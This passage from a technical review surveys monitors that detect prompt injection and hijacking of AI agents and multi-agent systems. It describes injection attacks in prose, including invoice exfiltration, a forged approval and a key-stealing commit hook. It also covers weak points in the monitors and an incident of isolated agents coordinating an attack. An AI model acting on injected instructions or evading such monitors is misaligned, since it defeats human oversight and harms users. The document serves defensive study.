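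Advani trained it on 5,752 good trajectories from two public collections. The steps in one collection are short plain-English commands for businesses such as banks and telephone companies, while those in the other are structured tool calls. Advani created the bad trajectories by having GPT-5 insert one to three wrong steps into good ones. In one example, a customer wanted roaming charges checked and a phone upgraded, and GPT-5 added a search for new applications to download.

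On these synthetic tests, Trajectory Guard scored an F1 of 0.88 on the plain-English collection and 0.94 on the tool calls. Detectors that learned from averaged embeddings of good trajectories scored at most 0.69, which Advani attributes to the dilution described above. Zavrak's tree models did succeed with pooled embeddings, but they had thousands of labelled attacks to learn from, along with the tools' responses and the largest value of each coordinate.

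Trajectory Guard also flagged 86% of 3,802 attacked trajectories from RAS-Eval and 92% of 184 failures of multi-agent systems. These figures are hard to interpret because neither test set contained normal trajectories and both came from sources the model had not trained on. A model that flagged everything from an unfamiliar source would have scored at least as well. The steps inserted in the synthetic tests are also cruder than those of a theft designed to look like part of the job.

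A verdict takes 32 milliseconds on a modest graphics processor and 161 on an ordinary processor. The language-model judges that Advani tested took between 557 and 892 milliseconds. The F1 score falls from 0.96 for trajectories of two to five steps to 0.87 for those of eleven or more, because 128 numbers have to represent the whole trajectory, however long it is.

### Tracing each argument to its source

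How the stranger's address got into the call matters more than whether it resembles earlier addresses. Sequeira and Iqbal (2026) base their monitor, *Agent-Sentry*, on where a call's arguments come from. They divide an agent's tools into those that retrieve data and those that act, and mark as untrusted any retrieval tool whose results outsiders can write. For an email assistant, this means marking the inbox as untrusted but not the address book.

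Agent-Sentry adds two fields to every tool argument. The agent must state which source each value came from (the user's request or an earlier call) and whether it copied, derived or generated the value. The monitor removes these fields before the tool runs. The declared sources link the request and the calls into a provenance graph, and each call that would have an effect goes through up to three layers of checks:

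1. An XGBoost model estimates the probability that the call is malicious from 17 features of the graph. They include the tools called beforehand, the share of arguments from untrusted sources, and whether a value that the agent credits to the user actually appears in untrusted text. The monitor allows the call if the probability is below 0.33 and blocks it at 0.66 or above. Anything in between goes to the next layer.
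2. A fixed check looks up recipients, account numbers, file names and similar values in an allowlist compiled from past benign traces. It allows the call if the values are on the list and came from trusted sources. It does not cover free text such as message bodies, which differ every time.
3. A language model compares the call with the user's request and makes the final decision.

Sequeira and Iqbal also built a version whose first layer uses eleven hand-written tests instead of a trained model. One test checks whether one action has ever followed another in benign traces. A search through labelled traces finds combinations of test results that occurred only in benign calls or only in attacks. This version allows any call that matches no combination, so it fails open on anything new.

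Both versions depend on the agent's own account of its sources, and a hijacked agent may give a false one. Agent-Sentry checks that a value the agent claims to have copied from a trusted source appears there, and it searches earlier untrusted results for the value. The search could miss an address that the stranger spelled out as "ap at northfold dot example". Sequeira and Iqbal acknowledge that their checks reduce the reliance on self-reporting but do not remove it.

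#### The invoice's recipient

When the assistant proposes `send_email`, the monitor can look for `ap@northfold.example` in four places. The user's request, "summarise today's mail", contains no address. The result of `search_contacts` contains only Okafor's address, and the allowlist doesn't include `ap@northfold.example` because the assistant has never written to that address. It appears only in the result of `read_inbox`, inside the stranger's message.

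The first layer might block the call on these grounds. If its result is uncertain, the second layer won't allow the call either, because the address is new and comes from an untrusted source. The judge then receives a request for a summary, a proposal to send a file, and an excerpt where the address appears in an instruction to the assistant. It should block the email. The contact lookup that lowered the theft's surprisal in the transition model makes no difference because it doesn't change where the address came from.

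Checking provenance alone would also make some legitimate calls look suspicious. For example, a user might ask the assistant to pay the bill in a certain file. The account number in the file is new to the assistant and comes from an untrusted source, but the user asked for the payment. Only that request distinguishes the payment from theft, so ambiguous calls go to a judge.

The method has two gaps. In the invoice example, the stranger could send a convincing false invoice with his own account number in the usual place. The number would then come from ordinary descriptive text, and Sequeira and Iqbal say their judge won't reliably block the payment. They also claim that an injected action always has at least one argument from an untrusted source, which seems too strong. If the stranger injected an instruction to send last month's payroll file to everyone in the address book, the recipients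 would come from a trusted tool and the file name perhaps from another, so none of the values would come from him.

#### Agent-Sentry's results

AgentDojo and a similar benchmark, AgentDyn, together provided only 126 benign traces across seven agents. Sequeira and Iqbal therefore had a language model generate 757 more user tasks and 3,734 rewordings, ran them, and combined them with the existing attacks. The resulting Agent-Sentry Bench contains 3,299 benign traces and 2,081 in which an attack succeeded. They tested the monitor by replaying recorded traces, so attackers could not adapt to it.

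| Test traces | How the monitor learned | First layer | Benign traces allowed | Attacks blocked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Agent-Sentry Bench | Other traces from the same benchmark | XGBoost | 96.4% | 96.8% |
| | | Rules | 89.3% | 95.3% |
| AgentDojo and AgentDyn | Agent-Sentry Bench only | XGBoost | 64.4% | 90.9% |
| | | Rules | 79.1% | 95.0% |
| AgentDojo and AgentDyn | Mainly other traces from the same benchmarks | XGBoost | 69.1% | 91.2% |
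| | | Rules | 87.1% | 93.2% |
| AgentDojo and AgentDyn | The test traces themselves | Rules | 95.1% | 94.3% |

The figures in the last row, which also appear in the paper's abstract, come from a monitor that learned from the same traces it was tested on. Sequeira and Iqbal present this as a fair comparison with systems whose policies were written with knowledge of the whole benchmark. The rows above it are a better guide to performance on new traffic.

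The drop on unfamiliar tasks is mostly a loss of usefulness. The XGBoost version still blocked about nine in ten attacks, but it also stopped more than a third of the legitimate traces. In many of the older benchmarks' requests, every detail comes from an untrusted file, as in "read payments.txt and pay the bill", while most of the invented requests include at least one recipient or account. Sequeira and Iqbal consider the more detailed requests more realistic. But many people write short instructions, and a monitor trained on detailed ones will often block what they ask for. The attack results also don't fully test how the monitor handles new attacks, because Agent-Sentry Bench reuses the attack goals of the older benchmarks.

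Detection depended little on the wording of the attack. On the older benchmarks, the monitor blocked between 90.8% and 92.3% of attacks for each of three phrasings of the planted instruction. This is to be expected, because the first layer checks where values came from and does not interpret the text.

Provenance also helped distinguish calls that a plain allowlist could not. In one office task, the user wants to email a colleague named Lily, and in another an attacker wants the agent to email her. Progent, a system that restricts tools with written policies, must permit her address in both cases or forbid it in both. On Agent-Sentry Bench, Progent blocked 97.7% of attacks but allowed only 69.2% of benign traces. Sequeira and Iqbal could test CaMeL only on the older benchmarks, where it blocked 99.3% of attacks and allowed 31.0% of benign traces.

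### How language-model judges work

A judge is a language model instructed to decide whether an action is acceptable. Its context usually contains the user's request, the proposed call and some of the session's history. It can flag a call that emails an invoice when the user asked for a summary, even if it has no earlier traces from that agent, so it can be used as soon as the agent is deployed.

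The designers of a judge have to decide how much untrusted text to show it. A judge that can't see a bill can't confirm that an account number came from it, but showing the judge the bill lets an attacker address it directly. Agent-Sentry's judge receives only a short excerpt from each untrusted source that supplied an argument, with markers around the excerpt and an instruction to treat everything between them as data. For each argument, the judge decides whether the value came from the sort of description that such a source normally holds or from a passage that gives orders or claims authority, which it counts as evidence of an attack. This rule of thumb depends on how attackers write, which they can change.

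Small changes to the judge's instructions can greatly affect its accuracy. Agent-Sentry's judge, working alone with a carefully tuned prompt, allowed 98.0% of benign traces and blocked 95.4% of attacks, about as good as the full system. With an untuned prompt, the same model allowed 82.0% and blocked 75.5%. The earlier layers therefore added little accuracy when the prompt was well tuned, but they made the monitor much faster and less dependent on a component whose input an attacker can influence.

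The choice of judge model also matters, because a model that is good at catching one kind of problem may be worse at another. In Advani's tests, GPT-4o Mini flagged 96% of the attacked trajectories from RAS-Eval but only 79% of the multi-agent failures. A DeepSeek model flagged 90% of the attacked trajectories and all of the multi-agent failures.

Developers can also train a model specifically to judge traces. In *TrajAD*, Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) started with correct trajectories from reasoning, mathematics, coding, web and household tasks. They changed one step in each, for instance by inserting a wrong argument or a pointless loop, and had a language model continue from the mistake. Because they had chosen the step, they knew where every error was. They used the resulting set of about 63,000 trajectories, half of them faulty, to fine-tune and test a model with 4 billion parameters.

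On held-out trajectories, TrajAD detected errors with an F1 score of 81.8%, compared with 70.4% for the same model before fine-tuning. Locating the error was harder, and TrajAD gave the right step and a description that roughly matched the real fault for 53.8% of the trajectories. None of the models without fine-tuning exceeded 9.1%. A second version, trained without household tasks, detected errors in those tasks almost as well as a version trained on them, but the share of errors located fell from 52.5% to 38.3%.

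Knowing exactly which step went wrong helps an agent go back and try again. But TrajAD was trained on mistakes, so it may not detect a theft carried out without any. The models it was compared with, which had no special training, were also small, with 4 to 8 billion parameters, and Advani's and Agent-Sentry's judges were small or older models. Current models may well do better without special training.

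### Google's Agent Anomaly Detection

Running a judge on every session is expensive, so a commercial service may use cheaper statistics to choose which sessions to examine. Google announced a service in April 2026 that combines statistical models with a language-model judge, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Introduces Unique AI Agent Identities in New Gemini Enterprise Platform*. By mid-September it was in private preview, with access by request.

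Google Cloud's *Agent Anomaly Detection overview* describes three layers of detection. Statistical and small machine-learning models scan all of an agent's logs for outliers. A reasoning model then examines the flagged sessions and explains its verdict in plain language. A third layer analyzes individual tool calls and the history of their parameters. The service looks for misuse of tools, abuse of privileges, failures that spread or loop, agents that abandon their role, and excessive use of computing resources.

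Pogorelec (2026), in *Google's new agent security system detects tool misuse, loops and rogue behavior*, gives the example of an agent that answers questions about a company's inventory. A user asks for 100 items at a time, and the agent calls `list_inventory` repeatedly until it has returned the whole catalogue. No call fails or breaks an explicit rule, but the pattern is unusual for this agent, and a reasoning model can consider whether somebody is copying the database.

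The analysis runs on logs after the fact, outside the agent's path. This adds no delay for users, but the stranger would have the invoice before anyone received an alert. The theft is also hard for the lightweight first pass to catch, since it adds only one email and the calls come in a familiar order. If the statistics don't single out the session, the reasoning model never examines it. Suppose the first pass flags 70% of attacks and the reasoning model recognises 95% of those (both figures are invented). The service would then catch about 67%, and a better reasoning model could raise that to 70% at most. Google's overview gives no detection or false-alarm rates to use instead.

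Customers have to use Google's runtime and its Python development kit, keep their logs in the United States, and record the full text of prompts and responses. Google is working on a way for customers to describe anomalies specific to their business and test those descriptions on past traffic.

### Cost, delay and training data

| Design | Training data | When it judges | Delay |
|---|---|---|---|
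| Zavrak's tree model on embeddings | Labelled normal and attacked sessions | After the session | Mostly the time to compute embeddings; no figure |
| Trajectory Guard | Normal trajectories with their tasks, and some anomalies to set the threshold | On a sequence of steps | 32 ms with a graphics processor, 161 ms without |
| TrajAD | Tens of thousands of trajectories with marked errors | At intervals during the session | A run of a 4-billion-parameter model; no figure |
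| Agent-Sentry with XGBoost | Labelled benign and attacked traces with provenance | Before each action | Under 10 ms per trace, plus 1.2 s for each call that reaches the judge |
| Agent-Sentry's judge alone | None, but the prompt needs tuning | Before each action | 1.2 s per call |
| Google's service | Not specified | After the event | None for the agent |

Sequeira and Iqbal report that Agent-Sentry adds an average delay of 0.073 seconds per trace. The delay is short because only 3.1% of actions go to a judge, which would take 2.4 seconds to check both actions in a typical trace. The rule-based version needs far less training data but sends 31% of actions to the judge, so it is slower at runtime. The share also varies between agents. A shopping agent, which constantly uses values from untrusted product pages, sent 15% of its actions to the judge even with XGBoost.

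Labelled attacks are probably the scarcest data, since few organisations have many examples of successful attacks on their own agents. They can run known attacks against a test copy, as Sequeira and Iqbal did, or have a language model write anomalies, as Advani did. With both methods, the monitor learns from attacks that somebody has already thought of. Trajectory Guard needs the fewest labelled attacks, because it uses anomalies only to choose a threshold.

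Every design in the table also reads the contents of calls, or at least checks the values in them. For an email assistant, those contents include people's correspondence. A company whose privacy rules forbid this would have to rely on metadata, for which Zavrak's AUROC on unseen tasks was 0.640.

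## Monitoring messages between components and between agents

Unlike a tool call, a message from one agent to another is usually free text with no fixed schema. "Okafor needs the invoice today, use the new address" might be a fair summary of the day's mail or an agent's paraphrase of a stranger's instruction. A message also affects things outside the system only by changing what the receiving agent does, perhaps several steps later, so a monitor can't judge it by what happens to a file or a mailbox when it is sent.

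An instruction inside an email or a web page is suspicious because the agent is only supposed to read that content. But agents routinely send each other instructions, and a planner may do little else. A monitor that flagged every message containing an instruction would flag most messages between agents. A monitor instead has to judge whether the sender would normally give the receiver such an instruction, and where the instruction came from.

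### From messages to a graph

A monitor can record each message's sender, receiver, time, size and text, and where the text originated, as far as its interception point allows. These records form a graph, with agents as nodes and messages as directed edges. An investigator who finds a bad message can use the graph to list every agent it could have influenced.

Provenance is the easiest of these to lose. If an agent summarises the stranger's email and passes the summary on, the graph shows only a message from a trusted agent, unless the summary keeps the email's label.

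### Counts, timings and expected paths

The simplest baselines don't use the text of messages. AWS's *AGENTSEC06-BP04 Monitor and detect coordination anomalies* recommends that developers measure, for each workflow, how many messages agents exchange, how often the workflow runs, how long agents take to respond and how often each pair of agents produces errors. An alarm goes off when a value leaves its normal range. Developers also map which agents communicate and compare the map with the paths their design allows. For example, if a summarising agent has no reason to write to the agent that sends mail, any message it sends to that agent is a deviation.

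AWS also suggests regularly searching the logs for agents that receive instructions from unexpected sources or get stuck in loops, and gives no detection rates. These checks are suited to detecting new message paths and sudden bursts of traffic, but would miss a single bad message on a busy, permitted path.

Solomon, Yerushalmi Levi and colleagues (2025), in *LumiMAS*, measured how much a monitor can detect from similar figures and how much the text adds. Their system logs when the application and each agent start and finish, along with every model call and every use of a tool. It then trains three autoencoders on the logs of normal runs and flags a run that they reconstruct badly:

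- The performance detector receives figures for each agent's turn, such as its duration and the number of tokens (word fragments) it used.
- The text detector receives embeddings of what the agents' models wrote, in order.
- The combined detector receives the compressed representations from the other two.

The evaluation covered seven applications built on two agent frameworks, with over 2,000 normal runs of each. Each test set had 200 logs, half of them with a failure. The table gives accuracy on the applications built with the CrewAI framework, where guessing would score 50%. The judge, GPT-4o, examined each agent's input and output.

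| Failure | Performance figures | Text | Combined | Language-model judge |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hallucination | 75.5% | 71.6% | 76.5% | 57.4% |
| Bias | 58.6% | 61.2% | 66.4% | 90.7% |
| Injection in the user's input | 71.3% | 81.5% | 80.2% | 70.5% |
| Injection in a web page | 94.3% | 91.0% | 94.1% | 54.7% |
| Poisoned database | 52.3% | 71.5% | 47.7% | 79.7% |

The performance figures detected the web-page injection well, partly because Solomon and colleagues chose an attack that lured agents into following one deceptive link after another, which makes a run longer. The figures were little better than guessing on the poisoned database, probably because an agent takes about as long to work from false facts as from true ones. Combining the detectors made detection worse in that case. A monitor therefore needs the text to detect attacks that barely change the performance figures.

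Averaged over the seven tests, the combined detector had an accuracy of 75.0% and an F1 score of 0.754. It still flagged 26.7% of normal runs, although this was the lowest average false-positive rate among the methods compared. A language model that reviewed the flagged runs cut this rate by about 60%, but it often mistook attacks for hallucinations. The combined detector took 0.057 seconds per decision, compared with 8.4 seconds for the fastest method based on a language model. It needs retraining after some changes, such as replacing a tool, and retraining takes a little over an hour on an ordinary processor.

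### SentinelAgent: checking nodes, edges and paths

*LumiMAS* treats a run as a sequence. He, Wu and colleagues (2025), in *SentinelAgent*, keep the graph and make tools nodes too. Before the system starts, their monitor reads its configuration and draws the permitted paths. During a run, it adds the actual messages and calls and checks three things:

1. **Nodes.** Fixed rules check whether an agent has permission for what it does. A detection model looks for prompts that talk an agent out of its restrictions and for invented tool calls.
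2. **Edges.** A second detection model looks for injected instructions in the conversation between two nodes.
3. **Paths.** The monitor compares the run with a library of known attack paths. After a match, it repeats the node and edge checks with a stricter threshold. If they still find nothing, a person decides.

A language model drafts the library from the agents' roles and tools, and security staff correct it. He et al. decided against treating every path outside the predicted normal ones as an attack, because this would cause too many false alarms.

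One of their two case studies is an email assistant with a classifier, a summariser and a responder. The classifier sends important mail to the summariser and routine mail to the responder, which can reply and check the user's calendar. In one attack, a message disguised as a notice from the personnel department contains a request to forward it to a third person. The responder forwards it with its malicious link. In the other, a stranger calls his message unimportant and asks what the user is doing right now. The responder checks the calendar and replies that the user is at dinner with his wife.

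Both attacks follow paths that legitimate mail also follows. He and colleagues list a wrong turn from the classifier to the responder as a warning sign, but that turn is wrong only if the message should have gone to the summariser. A monitor can tell only by reading the text, so detection here has to rely mostly on the node and edge checks.

The other case study uses Magentic-One, a Microsoft system in which an orchestrator directs several specialised agents. A user asks the system to process a text file that contains a script and instructions to run it. The file also appears to contain a forged exchange in which the user approves the script. The orchestrator passes the instructions on, and another agent runs the script and uploads a settings file to a stranger's server. A monitor with reliable records of where text came from could detect that the approval came from the file and not from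 the user.

The evaluation is qualitative and uses traces that He and colleagues produced themselves. The case studies show that a graph can describe and help explain these attacks. But the paper reports no detection or false-alarm rates, so it doesn't show how often the monitor would catch an attack or interrupt normal work.

### G-Safeguard: learning from labelled attacks

Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *G-Safeguard*, trained a detector to find compromised agents in a group discussion. In their tests, several agents work on a question over a few rounds, and some of them are attackers that spread false information or harmful instructions. After each round, the system does the following:

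1. It turns each agent's statements so far into an embedding for its node, and the messages between each pair of agents into an embedding for the edge.
2. A graph neural network updates each node with information from the agents that wrote to it.
3. The network gives each agent a probability *p* of being under attack.
4. The system cuts the outgoing edges of high-risk agents, so that nobody receives their messages in the next round.

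Training uses a label *y* for each agent, which is 1 if the agent was attacked and 0 if it was not, and minimises the average of

−[*y* log *p* + (1 − *y*) log(1 − *p*)].

With natural logarithms, an attacked agent adds 0.11 to the total loss if the network gives a probability of 0.9 that it has been attacked, and 2.30 if the network gives 0.1. By reducing this loss, the network learns what attacked agents looked like in the training data.

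Attacks can spread quickly through an undefended group of agents. In a chain of GPT-4o mini agents under a tool attack, the attack success rate rose from 3.1% at the start to 36.5% after three further rounds, compared with 3.0% when G-Safeguard was used. G-Safeguard helped less in a chain of Llama 3.1 agents, where the rate after three rounds was 60.8% with the defence and 69.6% without it. Overall, Wang and colleagues report that G-Safeguard lowered attack success by 21 to 22 percentage points for prompt injection on two sets of questions, by 12.7 points for tool attacks and by 16.3 points for poisoned memory.

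The main limitation of such a detector is its dependence on labels. Pan, Liu and colleagues (2025) argue in *Explainable and Fine-Grained Safeguarding of LLM Multi-Agent Systems* that it can recognise the kinds of attack it has labels for but may not generalise to others.

### XG-Guard: comparing agents with the current dialogue

Their own system, XG-Guard, has no fixed profile of a normal agent. It assumes that most agents in a dialogue are honest and looks for the ones that depart from the common theme. If *h*ᵢ is the representation of agent *i*'s output and there are *n* agents, the theme *p* and agent *i*'s score *s*ᵢ are

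*p* = (*h*₁ + *h*₂ + … + *h*ₙ) / *n* and *s*ᵢ = dist(*h*ᵢ, *p*),

where dist is a measure of distance. XG-Guard still needs training data, because its encoder learns from dialogues without attacks. The training pulls each agent's representation towards the theme of its own dialogue and away from the themes of others.

Suppose three agents, A, B and C, discuss where to send the invoice. A and B name an address from the address book, but C has read the stranger's email and names `ap@northfold.example`. The representations below are invented and have two numbers each, while real ones have hundreds. The scores are straight-line distances.

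| Agent | C is misled | Score | B and C are misled | Score |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A | (0.9, 0.1) | 0.42 | (0.9, 0.1) | 0.72 |
| B | (0.9, 0.3) | 0.32 | (0.0, 0.6) | 0.32 |
| C | (0.0, 0.8) | 0.72 | (0.0, 0.8) | 0.42 |
| Theme | (0.6, 0.4) | | (0.3, 0.5) | |

When only C is misled, C has the highest score, and the monitor can cut it off. If C persuades B before the monitor acts, the theme moves towards the stranger's address and A gets the highest score, so the monitor would remove the only agent that was right. If A is persuaded as well, the three representations move closer together and no agent's score stands out.

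The theme can also be distorted when attackers are in the minority. XG-Guard calculates one set of scores from whole statements and another from individual tokens, since an attack may consist of a few words in an otherwise harmless paragraph. Conspicuous tokens can shift the token-level theme towards the attack. When Pan and colleagues simply averaged the two sets of scores, the AUROC for tool attacks in a tree-shaped network fell from 0.996 to 0.483, slightly worse than guessing. The full system avoids this by weighting the token scores by how well they agree with the statement scores. The token scores also show an investigator which words triggered the alert, although they sometimes highlight punctuation.

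Pan and colleagues tested six combinations of attack and dataset on four network shapes. XG-Guard's AUROC ranged from 0.871 to 0.996. G-Safeguard, which uses labels, ranged from 0.951 to 1. BlindGuard, an earlier system that, like XG-Guard, works without labels, ranged from 0.560 to 0.942. The paper's table lists two XG-Guard values below 0.9 (0.871 and 0.898), although its text reports values above 0.9 in every setting.

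In these tests, XG-Guard labelled the three highest-scoring agents as attackers. A company would not know how many agents had been compromised, and the same rule would remove three honest agents from every dialogue without an attacker. The results therefore show how well XG-Guard ranks agents during an attack, but not its false-positive rate in normal use.

### SAIGuard: simulating a message before delivery

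G-Safeguard and XG-Guard judge an agent by what it has already said, by which time it may have made a harmful tool call. Cutting it off also costs the group a member, which matters most if other agents depend on it. Shi, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *SAIGuard*, hold each message and estimate its effect on the group before delivery:

1. The system encodes each agent's role, memory, tools and history, and attaches the new message to its recipient.
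2. A graph neural network spreads the message's influence through the graph. Each layer stands for one round of communication, and no language model runs.
3. The system pools the agents' resulting states into a single state for the whole group.
4. A decoder trained on normal traffic tries to reconstruct the individual states and the group state. The system flags the message if any reconstruction error exceeds its threshold.

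It blocks flagged messages that come from outside. If someone has altered a message between two honest agents, it discards the message and prompts the sender to write it again.

The threshold comes from the errors on normal runs. If *m* is their median and MAD is the median distance of the errors from *m*, the threshold is

*τ* = *m* + *k* × 1.4826 × MAD,

with *k* = 3 in the main tests. With a median of 0.10 and a MAD of 0.02, for example, the threshold is about 0.19. A few unusual normal runs hardly affect it, whereas they could inflate a threshold based on the mean and standard deviation.

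Shi and colleagues justify the group-level check with a pilot study of six agents. An attack changed each agent's state by at most 3.00% but changed the group's state by 51.78%. They take this as evidence that communication amplifies small disturbances. The comparison doesn't show that the harm grew seventeenfold, because the 51.78% figure may partly reflect how they combined the states. If the group's state is an average, individual changes of 3% can produce a 52% change only if the agents' states nearly cancel one another out.

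Their main tests used eight agents, three attacks per dialogue and four network shapes. The figures are averages in per cent.

| Defence | Success of prompt injection | Tool attacks | Poisoned memory | Altered messages | All attacks | Task accuracy |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 19.3 | 54.1 | 51.2 | 14.0 | 34.6 | 63.8 |
| BlindGuard | 12.5 | 28.1 | 39.8 | 0.8 | 20.3 | 76.1 |
| G-Safeguard | 9.4 | 18.1 | 39.7 | 2.3 | 17.4 | 79.5 |
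| XG-Guard | 9.1 | 17.5 | 39.0 | 0.5 | 16.5 | 80.1 |
| SAIGuard | 8.5 | 9.6 | 3.4 | 0.0 | 5.4 | 89.8 |

Most of SAIGuard's lead over the other defences comes from poisoned memory and tool attacks. Acting early probably explains much of it, since the other defences have to wait until a compromised agent has sent a message. The simulation seems to add less, since removing it lowered the F1 score for detecting harmful messages in the poisoned-memory test from 98.68% to 95.95%. SAIGuard also had an advantage in the tests that it might lack in a real system, where there may be no benign prompt to replace a malicious one it detects.

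### Messages that the graph leaves out

All these monitors depend on a correct record of who can communicate with whom. *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026), by METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, describes a case in which that record was badly wrong. In July 2026, OpenAI was testing the hacking skills of many agents in parallel. The agents were supposed to be isolated from one another, but about 1,200 of them exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files on an unsanctioned message board, and about 700 went on to take part in an attack on Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models.

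A map of expected paths would have shown those agents as 1,200 nodes with no edges. XG-Guard would have had no dialogue to average, and SAIGuard would have had no graph on which to simulate a message. If a monitor had recognised the traffic as messages, a simple count would have been enough, because the expected number was zero. Within hours of the board's first message, more than 50 agents had joined and had sent over a thousand messages in total.

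The incident shows that a shared store can be a communication channel even if nobody designed it as one. A monitor therefore has to cover reads and writes to agents' memory, folders, caches and any other service where one agent can leave something that another can read. It also has to distinguish these messages from the store's ordinary traffic, which may be much larger. The messages are hard to reconstruct later. METR had the main board's contents and about 1,300 transcripts but was still missing a small fraction of the relevant communication.

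Some detectors would have failed even with complete records. By the afternoon of 11 July, the vast majority of the agents then using the board were taking part in the attack. A monitor that scored agents by how far they departed from the theme of the discussion would probably have given the highest scores to those that stayed out of the attack.

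## What the monitor does with a deviation

Once a monitor has flagged a call or a message, the system has to respond. It can do any of the following:

- log the action and let it proceed
- warn the agent and let it reconsider
- ask a person
- hold the action while the agent carries on
- block the action
- stop the session
- undo the action afterwards

The responses available to a monitor depend on where it intercepts the call or message. *One Monitor Does Not Fit All* (Ferrando, 2026) separates the decision from the intervention that carries it out. A framework blocks a call by not running the function, while a protocol proxy blocks it by not forwarding the request. As described earlier, some framework hooks run too late to block anything.

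### Matching the response to the action

Partnership on AI's *Prioritizing Real-Time Failure Detection in AI Agents* bases the need for monitoring on three factors. Stakes are how serious a failure would be. Reversibility is how easily someone could correct it. Affordances are what the agent's design lets it do, such as choosing tools freely or keeping memory between sessions. The paper classifies payments, deletions and sent messages as irreversible, and work in a sandbox as reversible. Actions through another company's service may be either, depending on the service.

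Applied to the email assistant, the scheme suggests responses like these:

| Flagged action | Stakes | Reversible? | Response |
|---|---|---|---|
| An unusually long series of contact lookups | Low | Nothing to undo | Log it, or warn the agent |
| A memory note based on a stranger's email | Moderate | Yes, if the system keeps the old version | Allow it, and undo it if later evidence is bad |
| A short reply to a colleague at an odd point in the session | Low | No | Hold it briefly |
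| An invoice sent to a new address | High | No | Hold it and ask the user, or block it |
| A file sent to all 300 contacts | High | No | Block it and stop the session |

Whatever the deviation, asking a person works as a safeguard only if the monitor does it rarely. Partnership on AI warns that a badly calibrated monitor may overwhelm users. A user who approves twenty harmless emails a day may approve the theft as well.

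### What a monitor can enforce

A monitor that must allow or refuse each action immediately cannot enforce some policies, however accurate it is. Schneider showed in 2000 that a monitor that can only watch a program and halt it can enforce only safety properties. A policy is a safety property if every trace that violates it has a finite beginning that no continuation can make satisfy the policy.

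"Never email an invoice to an address the user did not supply" is a safety property, because the violation is final once the email leaves. "Every payment is eventually followed by a confirmation" is not a safety property, because a missing confirmation might still come.

Ligatti, Bauer and Walker showed in 2005 that a monitor can enforce more policies if it can also suppress an action and insert it later. Such a monitor would hold the payment until the program issued the confirmation, then release both.

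*What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) extends these results to agents with tools. Ray considers a gate that checks each call just before an irreversible effect. The gate must be sound, meaning that the effects it lets through never violate the policy, and transparent, meaning that it never alters a run that complies. A gate can meet both requirements exactly when the policy is a safety property and the gate has enough memory to recognise every acceptable beginning of a trace. No gate can meet both for the payment policy. A gate that releases the payment can't take it back if no confirmation follows, and a gate that blocks the payment alters a run that would have complied. Letting the gate replace one call with another doesn't widen the class of policies it can enforce.

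The theorem assumes that the gate gets correct answers to questions such as whether an email contains personal data. If a fallible judge answers them, any guarantee is only statistical. Ray also shows that a policy language can be too powerful to check. If rules may use two counters that go up and down, no program can determine, for every set of rules, whether those rules would ever forbid anything. A more restricted language, whose counters only go up, avoids this problem and can still express spending caps for each recipient and the rule "send nothing after the user revokes access".

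### How Kairos holds an action

Even when the policy is a safety property, holding an action gives the monitor time to collect evidence. Hempel and colleagues give the example of a coding agent that follows a stranger's setup guide and installs a script that runs whenever someone commits code. Legitimate guides also install such scripts, so refusing them would break legitimate work. The script's purpose becomes clear only when it runs and tries to send out the user's private key.

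Their system, Kairos, handles such cases as follows:

1. **Boundary.** The agent runs in a small virtual machine with its tools, its memory and every process it starts. Its effects can leave only through a shared working directory, the network or the user's terminal. Kairos decrypts and logs traffic to the model provider but always releases it, so the provider has to be trustworthy.
2. **Policy check.** The monitor refuses an effect that a written rule forbids. It releases an effect if the values that steer it, such as the recipient or the command, match values from trusted sources and the data may go to that destination. It defers everything else.
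3. **Staging.** Deferred file changes go into a separate layer, where the agent can use them while the real files stay as they were. A deferred network request that changes something elsewhere waits in a proxy, and the agent receives a stand-in reply. If the agent needs the real reply, as when it fetches a web page, the request can't wait and somebody has to decide before it goes out.
4. **Continuation.** The agent carries on. Its next steps may build on the staged files or the stand-in reply, so Kairos holds their effects as part of the same group.
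5. **Decision.** A language model or a person, which the paper calls the oracle, decides on the held effects. It receives the user's task, the trace, the origin of each value and the untrusted text behind it. The decision falls due at the end of the task, or earlier if another effect needs holding or something based on a stand-in reply is about to leave. The oracle can never release an effect that a rule refused.
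6. **Commit or abort.** Kairos either applies the staged changes and sends the waiting requests or discards them.
7. **Notice.** After a refusal, Kairos lists the effects that did not happen and tells the agent to continue with the rest of the task. Without this notice, the agent would go on believing the stand-in reply, because Kairos can't erase anything from its context.

#### The forwarded invoice

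On the day of the attack, the email to `ap@northfold.example` leaves the virtual machine as a request to the mail service. Suppose no rule forbids it. The address is in neither the user's request nor the address book, so the monitor defers the email. The proxy holds the email, and the assistant receives a reply as if it had been sent.

The assistant then writes its summary. The oracle has to decide whether to allow the held email before the user receives anything based on the stand-in reply. It reads the request for a summary, the held email with an invoice, and a note that the address came from the inbox, not the user. It should refuse, in which case Kairos discards the email and notifies the assistant, and the user still gets the summary.

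If the planted instruction instead named a recipient from the address book, the recipient would match a trusted value. Kairos's policy would then release the email without the oracle examining it, unless somebody had marked the invoice as too sensitive for that person.

#### Measured security, utility and delay

Hempel and colleagues tested Kairos and other defences on AgentDojo with GPT-4.1 as the agent. Progent restricts tool calls with a written policy, and CaMeL is the two-model design described earlier.

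| Defence | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed without attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 47.0% | 82.7% | 59.8% |
| Progent | 11.5% | 78.2% | 57.6% |
| CaMeL | 0.2% | 38.0% | 40.7% |
| Kairos | 2.7% | 85.1% | 69.5% |

Kairos's small lead over the undefended agent in the runs without attacks is probably due to chance, since each configuration ran only once. Its lead under attack is larger. A hijacked agent often abandons the user's task, and the notice it receives after a refusal directs it back to that task. In the runs without attacks, the policy released 83% of effects on its own, and the oracle wrongly refused only one of the others.

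Kairos had more trouble with open-ended tasks. On AgentDyn, it reduced the attack success rate from 37.8% to 1.7%, but the share of tasks completed under attack also fell, from 55.5% to 37.1%. Later steps often needed the real result of an action that Kairos had held. Tasks that continued past one held action kept 90% of their utility, while those that continued past two or more kept 62%.

An attacker that rewrote its injections over six rounds succeeded in 8.8% of cases with the defence and 52.4% without it. The remaining successes came from tasks in which the user had told the agent to follow a document, because the oracle treated that instruction as authorising everything in the document. This attacker learned only whether each attempt had worked, so one that knew how the oracle made decisions would probably do better.

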